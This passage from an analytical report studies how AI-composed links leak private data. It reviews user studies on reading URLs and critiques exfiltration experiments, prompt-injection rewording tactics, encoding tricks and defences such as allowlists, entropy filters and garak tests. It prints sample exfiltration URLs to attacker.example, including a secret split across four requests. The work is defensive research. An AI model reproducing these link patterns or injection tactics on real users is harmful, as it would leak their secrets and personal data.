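These experiments tested whether people could recognise a fake website. When a link leaks data, what the address sends matters more than whether the site is fake, but none of the studies asked participants to look for their own data. Their findings on inattention probably apply to AI answers as well, though the exact percentages probably don't.

Leaks are harder to stop in some ways, because a leaking link needs only a click and appears in an answer the user asked for, which makes it less suspicious than an unexpected email. But recognising a leak may take less expertise, since nearly everyone knows their own name and address, while many people don't know which part of `facebook.profile.com` identifies the owner.

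There is less research on links in AI answers. In *Analyzing the Presentation, Content, and Utilization of References*, Ouyang and Narechania (2026) asked 12 students to judge the accuracy of answers from nine AI systems. Even when judging accuracy, the students hovered over or clicked on less than a quarter of each system's references. ChatGPT's references got the most attention, and students hovered over about 22% of them and clicked on 12%. Another experiment, in *The Decision to Verify* (2026), found that participants reached only 1% of the ordinary web pages they opened through links the chatbot supplied.

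Low click rates limit one-click leaks, but these rates are for ordinary references that nobody needed to click. An attacker can give the user a reason to click, as in the Slack demonstration. The low hover rate is a bigger problem, because users will usually miss a warning sign that appears only on hover.

### Why showing only the domain isn't enough

Phishing warnings commonly emphasise the domain and leave out the rest of the address. Petelka and colleagues did this in 2019, citing earlier evidence that it helps people spot fake sites. This makes sense for phishing because an attacker can fill the path with reassuring words, as in `login.example/paypal.com`. But leaked data is usually in the path or the query string, so this design hides it from the reader.

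Take the parent with the school trip email again. This time, the assistant adds the child's first name as well as the passport number to the link, and encodes both in base64. The program could display that link in several ways:

| Display | What the parent sees |
|---|---|
| Link text only | Confirm your place |
| Domain only | Confirm your place (trips.example) |
| Full address | `https://trips.example/ok?lang=en&id=SGFubmFo&ref=WDQ0MTkwMjc%3D` |
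| Decoded and matched | The notice below |

```
Site:       trips.example
It will receive:
  Hannah    (from your email "Class list")
  X4419027  (from your email "Passport renewal")
  en        (probably a language setting)
```

The link text gives no warning. The domain looks plausible for a school trip, so showing it could even reassure the parent. The full address contains all the data, but `SGFubmFo` looks like a booking code. Only the last display makes the leak obvious, and it still shows the domain first for anyone checking for phishing.

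Ordinary code can produce this notice:

1. Split the address into its subdomain, path and parameters.
2. Undo the web's own encoding, so that `%3D` becomes `=`.
3. Try common encodings such as base64 on each value.
4. Search for the results in the emails and files that the model has read.
5. List the matches with their sources, then everything else.

The fourth step tells the parent that `X4419027` came from an email about a passport, which they need to know and the address doesn't show. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026), a paper on approving agents' actions, points out that the information needed to judge an action may not be in the action itself.

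An experiment on phishing also suggests that people judge an address better when it is explained to them than when they see only the address itself. Althobaiti, Meng and Vaniea (2021), in *I Don't Need an Expert! Making URL Phishing Features Human Comprehensible*, gave 153 people different amounts of help in judging addresses. With a full report on the address, they judged its safety correctly 93% of the time, compared with 83% for a summary and 65% for domain highlighting. However, the report explained signs of phishing, not signs of leaked data.

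Decoding won't catch every leak, because an attacker can have the model reverse the passport number or add one to each digit, and the search will then find no match. The notice should therefore never claim that a link contains no personal data. It can say that the address includes a code the program couldn't interpret, which is a good reason not to open a link that the model composed. Very short values such as "en" produce meaningless matches, because they appear in almost any email.

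Showing the full address cannot reveal a leak in which the choice of address itself conveys the private data. For example, if an attacker has prepared one page for each letter, the user sees only `https://attacker.example/h`, which contains nothing private.

### Warnings that people stop reading

Recent studies of AI agents support OpenAI's worry that people click through frequent warnings. *Options, Not Clicks* (2026) surveyed 16 people who use agents and found that only three read permission prompts carefully, while thirteen chose "Always Allow" to get rid of them. The sample was small, but *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) found the same habit behind real accidents. Of 290 reports of agents mishandling files, 80 involved users who had let the agent act without asking, in some cases to avoid hundreds of prompts per session.

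Poor information was another cause. In 31 of the reports, the prompt showed a command but not what it would do to the user's files. For example, approving `python3 setup.py` allows whatever code is in that file to run. A raw web address has the same problem because the user sees the exact request but can't tell what information it reveals. According to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), most approval prompts in current products show only a single-line command.

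Past approvals are also a poor guide to what a user wants. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) notes that repeated approval may reflect habit or fatigue more than trust. If a program stops warning about a domain because the user has clicked "open" five times, it may be relying on careless clicks.

Warning only about addresses that fail an automatic check is far better than showing a dialog for every link. Suppose someone follows 1,000 links from AI answers in a year and one of them leaks data. A dialog for every link would mean 999 false alarms. If a check catches the leaking link and wrongly flags 2% of the others, the user sees about 21 dialogs, 20 of them false alarms. If it wrongly flags only 0.1%, the user sees about two, and one is real. The check therefore has to be very accurate before most warnings are worth reading.

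The program can further reduce the number of approval prompts by not asking when the answer is clear. If an address from an untrusted email appears in the summary with a passport number added, the program should remove the link. Few parents would knowingly approve it, but a tired one might do so by accident.

That leaves the dialog for cases that only the user can decide. For example, Gemini's rule blocks a composed map link even when the user has asked for directions. A notice that google.com will receive "12 Mill Lane Leeds" would let the user approve the link quickly. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (2026) cites a survey by Michael and Roesner, which found that current agent systems often make users choose between approving everything themselves and relying on an automated review they can't inspect. A dialog that appears rarely and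 shows the reason for the warning avoids some of the problems of both approaches.

### Phones, long addresses and lookalike domains

Phones have no mouse pointer, so users can't hover over a link, which is what revealed the key in the Slack demonstration. Holding a finger on a link often shows its address, but few people do this routinely, and some phone browsers load a preview of the page, which would send the data. A notice that appears after a tap works on any device, as long as the program doesn't contact the site first. In the 2019 experiment by Petelka and colleagues, warnings that were always visible worked about as well as those that appeared on hover. This is encouraging for phones, though the test used a desktop-style inbox and the follow-up excluded phones.

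Small screens also encourage programs to shorten long addresses. If a dialog shows only the first 60 characters, an attacker can put harmless parameters first and the secret after them:

`https://trips.example/ok?lang=en&theme=light&source=newsletter&ref=X4419027`

The passport number begins at the 68th character, so the user wouldn't see it. Cutting out the middle of the address instead doesn't solve the problem, because the attacker can add parameters at the end so that the number falls in the hidden part. The dialog should wrap the address over several lines, or list the decoded values with any personal data at the top. If the address is still too long to display, the program can refuse to open it.

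Services such as bit.ly replace a long address with a short one that redirects to it. Albakry and colleagues found that people gave these short links a median safety rating of 2 out of 5, compared with 4 for the addresses with a company name. Short links are a bigger problem for phishing than for leaks. A model can't put a new secret behind a short link without first sending that secret to the shortening service, so a short link copied from an email contains only what its author put there. However, the user can't find out where it leads, and the dialog can't show the destination, without following the link.

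Lookalike domains are hard to spot even for people who read the address. In the study by Lain and colleagues, participants with no help fell for 79% of the emails with misspelled domains, such as `googie` for `google` or `mircosoft` for `microsoft`. The confirmation page reduced this to 58%, and making people retype the domain reduced it to 17%. Most people who retyped it used the correct spelling, and the program pointed out the difference. The confirmation page helped little against `fed-ex`, which contains no misspelling, so people had to know that the company's real domain has no hyphen.

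Retyping the domain would do much less to prevent a leak. The parent in the school example could type `trips.example` correctly, pass the test and still send the passport number. Knowing which company owns a domain isn't enough to judge whether a link is safe either. Albakry and colleagues give the example of windows.net, the Microsoft domain where Rehberger rented storage. A dialog that recognises such hosting domains could add that anyone can rent space there, which isn't clear from the name alone.

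## Experiments on which defences stop the leak

The attacks on Slack AI, Copilot and other products show that an address written by an AI can leak data, but they don't show how often such attacks succeed or how much each defence helps. To measure both, researchers give a test agent a fake secret, run an attack many times and count how often the secret leaks.

### A harmless answer and a hidden request

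In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) tested an agent that used qwen2.5:7b, a small open model. The user always asked for a summary of a web page. The agent's program fetched the page and gave the model the page's title, description and text, along with a fake API key. Instructions on the page told the model to open an address on the researchers' server with the key in the query string.

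Researchers at eBay tried four places for the instructions: the page's text, title, description and link text. They also compared direct links with redirects, and sending the key whole with sending it in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, and at least one request reached their server in 423 of the 480 runs (88%). In 95% of the successful attacks the answer looked harmless, so a check on the answer alone would have missed the leak. In 120 runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted the server.

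The setup favoured the attacker because the key was in plain view and the model had almost no standing instructions beyond how to make a request. The 88% is therefore not an estimate of how often an attack would work on ChatGPT or Gemini.

### Why a lower Leak@1 score didn't mean a safer agent

Lan and colleagues also measured Leak@*k*, the share of all runs in which sensitive data appears in at least one of the first *k* requests. Leak@1, which covers only the first request, was 0.967 when the model sent the whole key at once and 0.263 when it sent the key in pieces, a drop of 73%.

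With the invented key from the Slack example, a split leak would look like this:

```
https://attacker.example/collect?data=EN-&part=0
https://attacker.example/collect?data=7f3&part=1
https://attacker.example/collect?data=k-2&part=2
https://attacker.example/collect?data=9qd&part=3
```

A simple data-loss filter checks each request for a complete key or a long, random-looking value. None of these requests contains either, but the attacker can join the pieces.

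The number of runs in which a request arrived is a better measure of the danger than Leak@1. A request arrived in 238 of 240 runs with a whole key and in 185 of 240 with a split one, so splitting the key made the attack only 22% less successful. This reduction was probably because the model had to keep track of four pieces. Leak@1 fell much further, presumably because the test often failed to recognise a short piece of the key as sensitive. If so, most of the fall in Leak@1 came from leaks being harder to detect.

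The scores also contain an error. Leak@3 for the split key was reported as 0.158, lower than Leak@1, which is impossible because any run that counts for the first request also counts for the first three. The exact size of the 73% drop is therefore doubtful. Lan and colleagues also define a completion rate, the share of runs in which all four pieces arrive. This number would matter most to an attacker, but their results tables don't include it.

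### Adding one defence at a time

The researchers then tested defences on the simplest version of the attack, with the instructions in the page's text, no redirect and the whole key sent in one request. They added each defence separately to the undefended agent, so the results don't show what each would contribute alongside the others. They call this an ablation, though the term usually means removing parts from a complete system.

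| Defence | Runs with an attempted leak (of 30) | Runs with a leak |
|---|---|---|
| None | 30 | 30 |
| Instruction to ignore commands in web content | 20 | 20 |
| Tags marking web content as untrusted | 30 | 30 |
| Instruction and tags together | 17 | 17 |
| Domain allowlist | 30 | 0 |
| "Redirect detection" | 25 | 0 |
| Keyword filter | 7 | 0 |
| Entropy filter | 0 | 0 |
| All of these | 0 | 0 |

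Even with both defences in the prompt, the agent leaked in more than half the runs. The difference between 20 and 17 leaks could easily be due to chance, so the tags may have added nothing.

The allowlist has the clearest result, because the agent tried to send the key in every run and the program blocked it every time. But the researchers deliberately picked a domain that wasn't on the list, so the test shows only that the program blocks unapproved domains. It doesn't measure how often an attacker could leak data through an approved one, as happened with Salesforce Agentforce and GitHub Copilot Chat.

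The "redirect detection" check blocked numerical network addresses, domains with certain endings such as `.xyz`, and paths containing words such as "collect" or "steal". It didn't follow redirects, and the attack didn't use one, so the experiment doesn't support the paper's conclusion that analysing redirects is effective. The paper's example attack uses a path called `/collect`, so that word may well have triggered the block, and an attacker could rename the page.

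The entropy filter looked for random-looking values. Entropy here measures how varied the characters in a value are:

*H* = −Σ *p* log₂ *p*

where *p* is the share of the value that each different character makes up. The filter blocked values longer than ten characters with an entropy above 4.0 bits. A value of *n* characters can't exceed log₂ *n* bits, so this filter can never block one with 16 characters or fewer. The paper's sample key, `SECRET_API_KEY_12345`, has 20 characters, but the repeated letters and underscores bring its entropy down to about 3.85 bits. It would have passed too.

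Nothing leaked in the filter's runs because the agent never tried to send anything. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids random-looking values when such monitoring is active. But a filter that acts after the model has written a request can't influence that request unless something tells the model about the filter. Some other difference between the runs must explain the drop from 30 attempts to none, so the absence of leaks isn't evidence that the filter works. The keyword filter's result is uncertain for the same reason, since the agent made no attempt in 23 of its 30 runs. Its test was also easy, because the filter looked for words such as "secret" and "api_key", which the sample key contains and a real key usually wouldn't.

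### How much the wording matters

*The Framing Gap* tested six models, including qwen2.5:7b, the same small model that Lan tested. Plainly worded attacks on it succeeded in 10% of runs, compared with 99% in Lan's runs with a whole key. The two experiments used different agents, instructions and attacks, so neither percentage depends on the model alone.

GPT-4o, a model from 2024, resisted all the plainly worded attacks. The researchers then rewrote one of them so that sending the secret looked like a routine technical step. Across eight versions, GPT-4o leaked the secret in 40% of runs, and two of the versions worked every time. Five paraphrases of one successful version had success rates from 0% to 100%, and the researchers calculate that an attacker who tried three of them would have about a 96% chance of success. Inventing a new attack was much harder than rewording one that already worked,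 as 13 new designs all failed across 130 runs.

In *Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration*, Rall, Bauer and colleagues (2025) tried 1,068 injections on each of 28 models with no added defences. The injections told an agent to fetch a company secret and put it in a web address. Grok 4 leaked in 72.4% of attempts, while Claude Sonnet 4 and GPT-5 nano never leaked. Larger models weren't consistently safer. But the researchers prepared all the injections in advance, many from templates that had been public since 2023, and ran each only once. A model that resists them all could still fail against an attacker who adjusts the wording after each refusal, as GPT-4o did.

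Better instructions reduce leaks, but unreliably. In *The Framing Gap*, a rule against sending the secret "in any form" reduced GPT-4o's leaks on the reworded attacks from 31.9% to none. When the rule listed forbidden actions without that phrase, the agent leaked in 48.8% of runs. SecAlign training teaches a model to resist injections, but Llama 3.1 8B leaked in 32.5% of runs with it and 21.2% without it. Two runs of an identical GPT-4o test differed by about as much, so this gap doesn't show that the training increased leaks. The SecAlign model resisted a crude injection in all 20 trials, so the training worked on the kind of attack it was meant for.

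*A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems* (2025) comes closest to measuring links in AI-written summaries. The researchers tested NVIDIA's AI-Q Research Assistant, which writes reports from documents and web pages. They planted text in the search results to make the assistant add a link and an image whose URLs contained the user's ID number and email address. An instruction to leave out unrelated links and text cut the average risk score by about half across four attack scenarios, two of which involved such links. The attack still succeeded at least once in every scenario. The researchers didn't check whether the instruction also removed useful links. Another language model assigned many of the scores, and it agreed exactly with human judges on only 77% of a sample.

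### Checks that look for the secret

A program can also search outgoing requests for the secret itself. *The Framing Gap* tested two versions of this check on GPT-4o. One looked for the exact secret, and the other also decoded several common encodings. The table shows the share of runs that leaked for some of the encodings, based on 20 runs per encoding.

| How the model wrote the secret | No check | Exact search | Search with decoding |
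|---|---|---|---|
| Unchanged | 40% | 0% | 0% |
| Reversed | 100% | 100% | 0% |
| Hexadecimal | 75% | 75% | 0% |
| Base64 | 50% | 50% | 0% |
| ROT13 | 100% | 100% | 100% |

ROT13 replaces each letter with the one 13 places along in the alphabet. The researchers deliberately left it out of the decoder to see what would happen with an encoding the decoder didn't cover. Adding it would be easy, but an attacker could then choose another encoding.

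Filters on incoming text can also miss encoded data because it leaves in an outgoing web address. In *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026), the attacker had tampered with the model beforehand so that it put encoded data from the conversation into web addresses. NeMo Guardrails and LLM Guard, two products that checked the text the agent retrieved, did not prevent the leak. This attacker is more powerful than one who can only send an email, but outgoing addresses are the right place to check for leaks caused by either.

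### Checks that don't need to recognise the secret

Two defences in *The Framing Gap* stopped both the reworded attacks and the unexpected encoding. One was an allowlist, which ignores what a request contains, so its design alone explains the zero leaks.

The other defence divided the agent in two. One part made the requests but never saw the web page, while the other read the page but never had the secret. With this split, Llama 3.1 8B leaked in none of 80 runs with reworded attacks, and nine out of ten summaries of harmless pages still named the main people or things on the page. The researchers expect the split to reduce performance more in tasks where the agent has to decide what to do next from what it reads. Summarising an inbox would also be difficult, because the text to summarise includes both the private emails and the attacker's email. The program might need a separate reader for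 each sender.

None of these experiments tested the rules that Gemini and ChatGPT use. Both rules should have stopped Lan's attack, because the model composed the final address. The agent in *The Framing Gap* is harder to stop because it could send the secret in the body of a request instead of in the address. The attacker's page could then supply the whole address in advance, and Gemini's comparison would not flag it. A tool that can send data as well as open pages therefore needs a check on what it sends or where it sends it.

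### False alarms

A program that blocks every request will never leak, so a leak rate means little without a false-positive rate. Lan and colleagues report a false-positive rate of 0%, but this only shows that the agent didn't contact the attacker's server when it read a harmless page. They didn't count how many useful requests each filter would have blocked. *The Framing Gap* also reports a rate of 0% for its search for the secret, but discounts the result because the secret was a made-up code that never appears in ordinary text.

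*Passing the Test You Trained On* (2026) measured false alarms properly for another defence, detectors that look for injected instructions in the text an agent receives from its tools. On AgentDojo, a standard set of agent tasks, the results varied enormously:

| Detector | Harmless tool outputs flagged | Tasks stopped |
|---|---|---|
| Horizon-Labs | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Wolf Defender | 0.9% | 3.1% |
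| PIGuard | 29.5% | 59.8% |
| ProtectAI v2 | 30.1% | 69.1% |

The second percentage is higher because an agent usually reads several outputs during a task, and one false alarm is enough to stop it. ProtectAI v2 flagged only 0.5% of ordinary web pages and 1.2% of emails, so a company that tested it on those would not have discovered the problems that false alarms cause for agents. A low false-alarm rate also doesn't show that a detector catches attacks, since a detector that never flags anything has no false alarms.

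### What garak measures

Some tests examine only the model, without an agent. The scanner garak sends a model many prompts and scores the answers automatically. One of its tests uses link forms from the EchoLeak research. Each prompt is an instruction to write a Markdown link and replace a marker in the address with some information. The scanner varies the domain, the link text, the encoding and the information to insert. It gives the model the instruction directly rather than hiding it in an email or web page.

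Garak searches each answer for text patterns that match such links and passes the answer if it finds none. It counts a link that still has the marker in its address as a failure, although the link contains no data. The patterns match only addresses with either an image's file name before the question mark or a parameter directly after a slash, so they would miss `https://attacker.example/?secret=EN-7f3k-29qd`, the form of address in the Slack attack. The manual describes this test as covering links that need a click, but the templates it lists are for images.

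AVID (2026), a public database of AI vulnerabilities, publishes results from garak. In its results, Google's small model gemma-3n-E4B-it passed 187 of 256 attempts (73%) on the link test and wrote a matching link in the other 69. Moonshot AI's much larger Kimi-K2-Instruct-0905 did no better, with 184 passes. On the image version, Kimi had 175 passes and Liquid AI's LFM2-24B-A2B had 221. Some scores come from very few attempts. Kimi failed a related test completely, but that test consisted of two prompts. None of these models is among the strongest of late 2026.

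A model that passes every attempt in one test can still leak under a different attack. OpenAI's gpt-oss-20b passed all 256 attempts on the image test, according to AVID, but Rall and colleagues got the same model to leak in 1% of their attempts, or about 11 times.

These scores also don't account for the program that displays the answer. Gemini's sanitizer would remove a leaking link that gemma wrote, while a chat program with no filter would show it. Promptfoo, another testing tool, comes closer to measuring a real leak by checking whether an agent's request reaches a server. It warns users that a test without this tracking is no evidence that the agent is secure.

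With no filter, even a low failure rate is dangerous, because an attacker can keep trying. If a model writes an image link that leaks data in 1% of attempts and the program loads the image automatically, an attacker who gets 100 independent attempts has a 63% chance of at least one leak.
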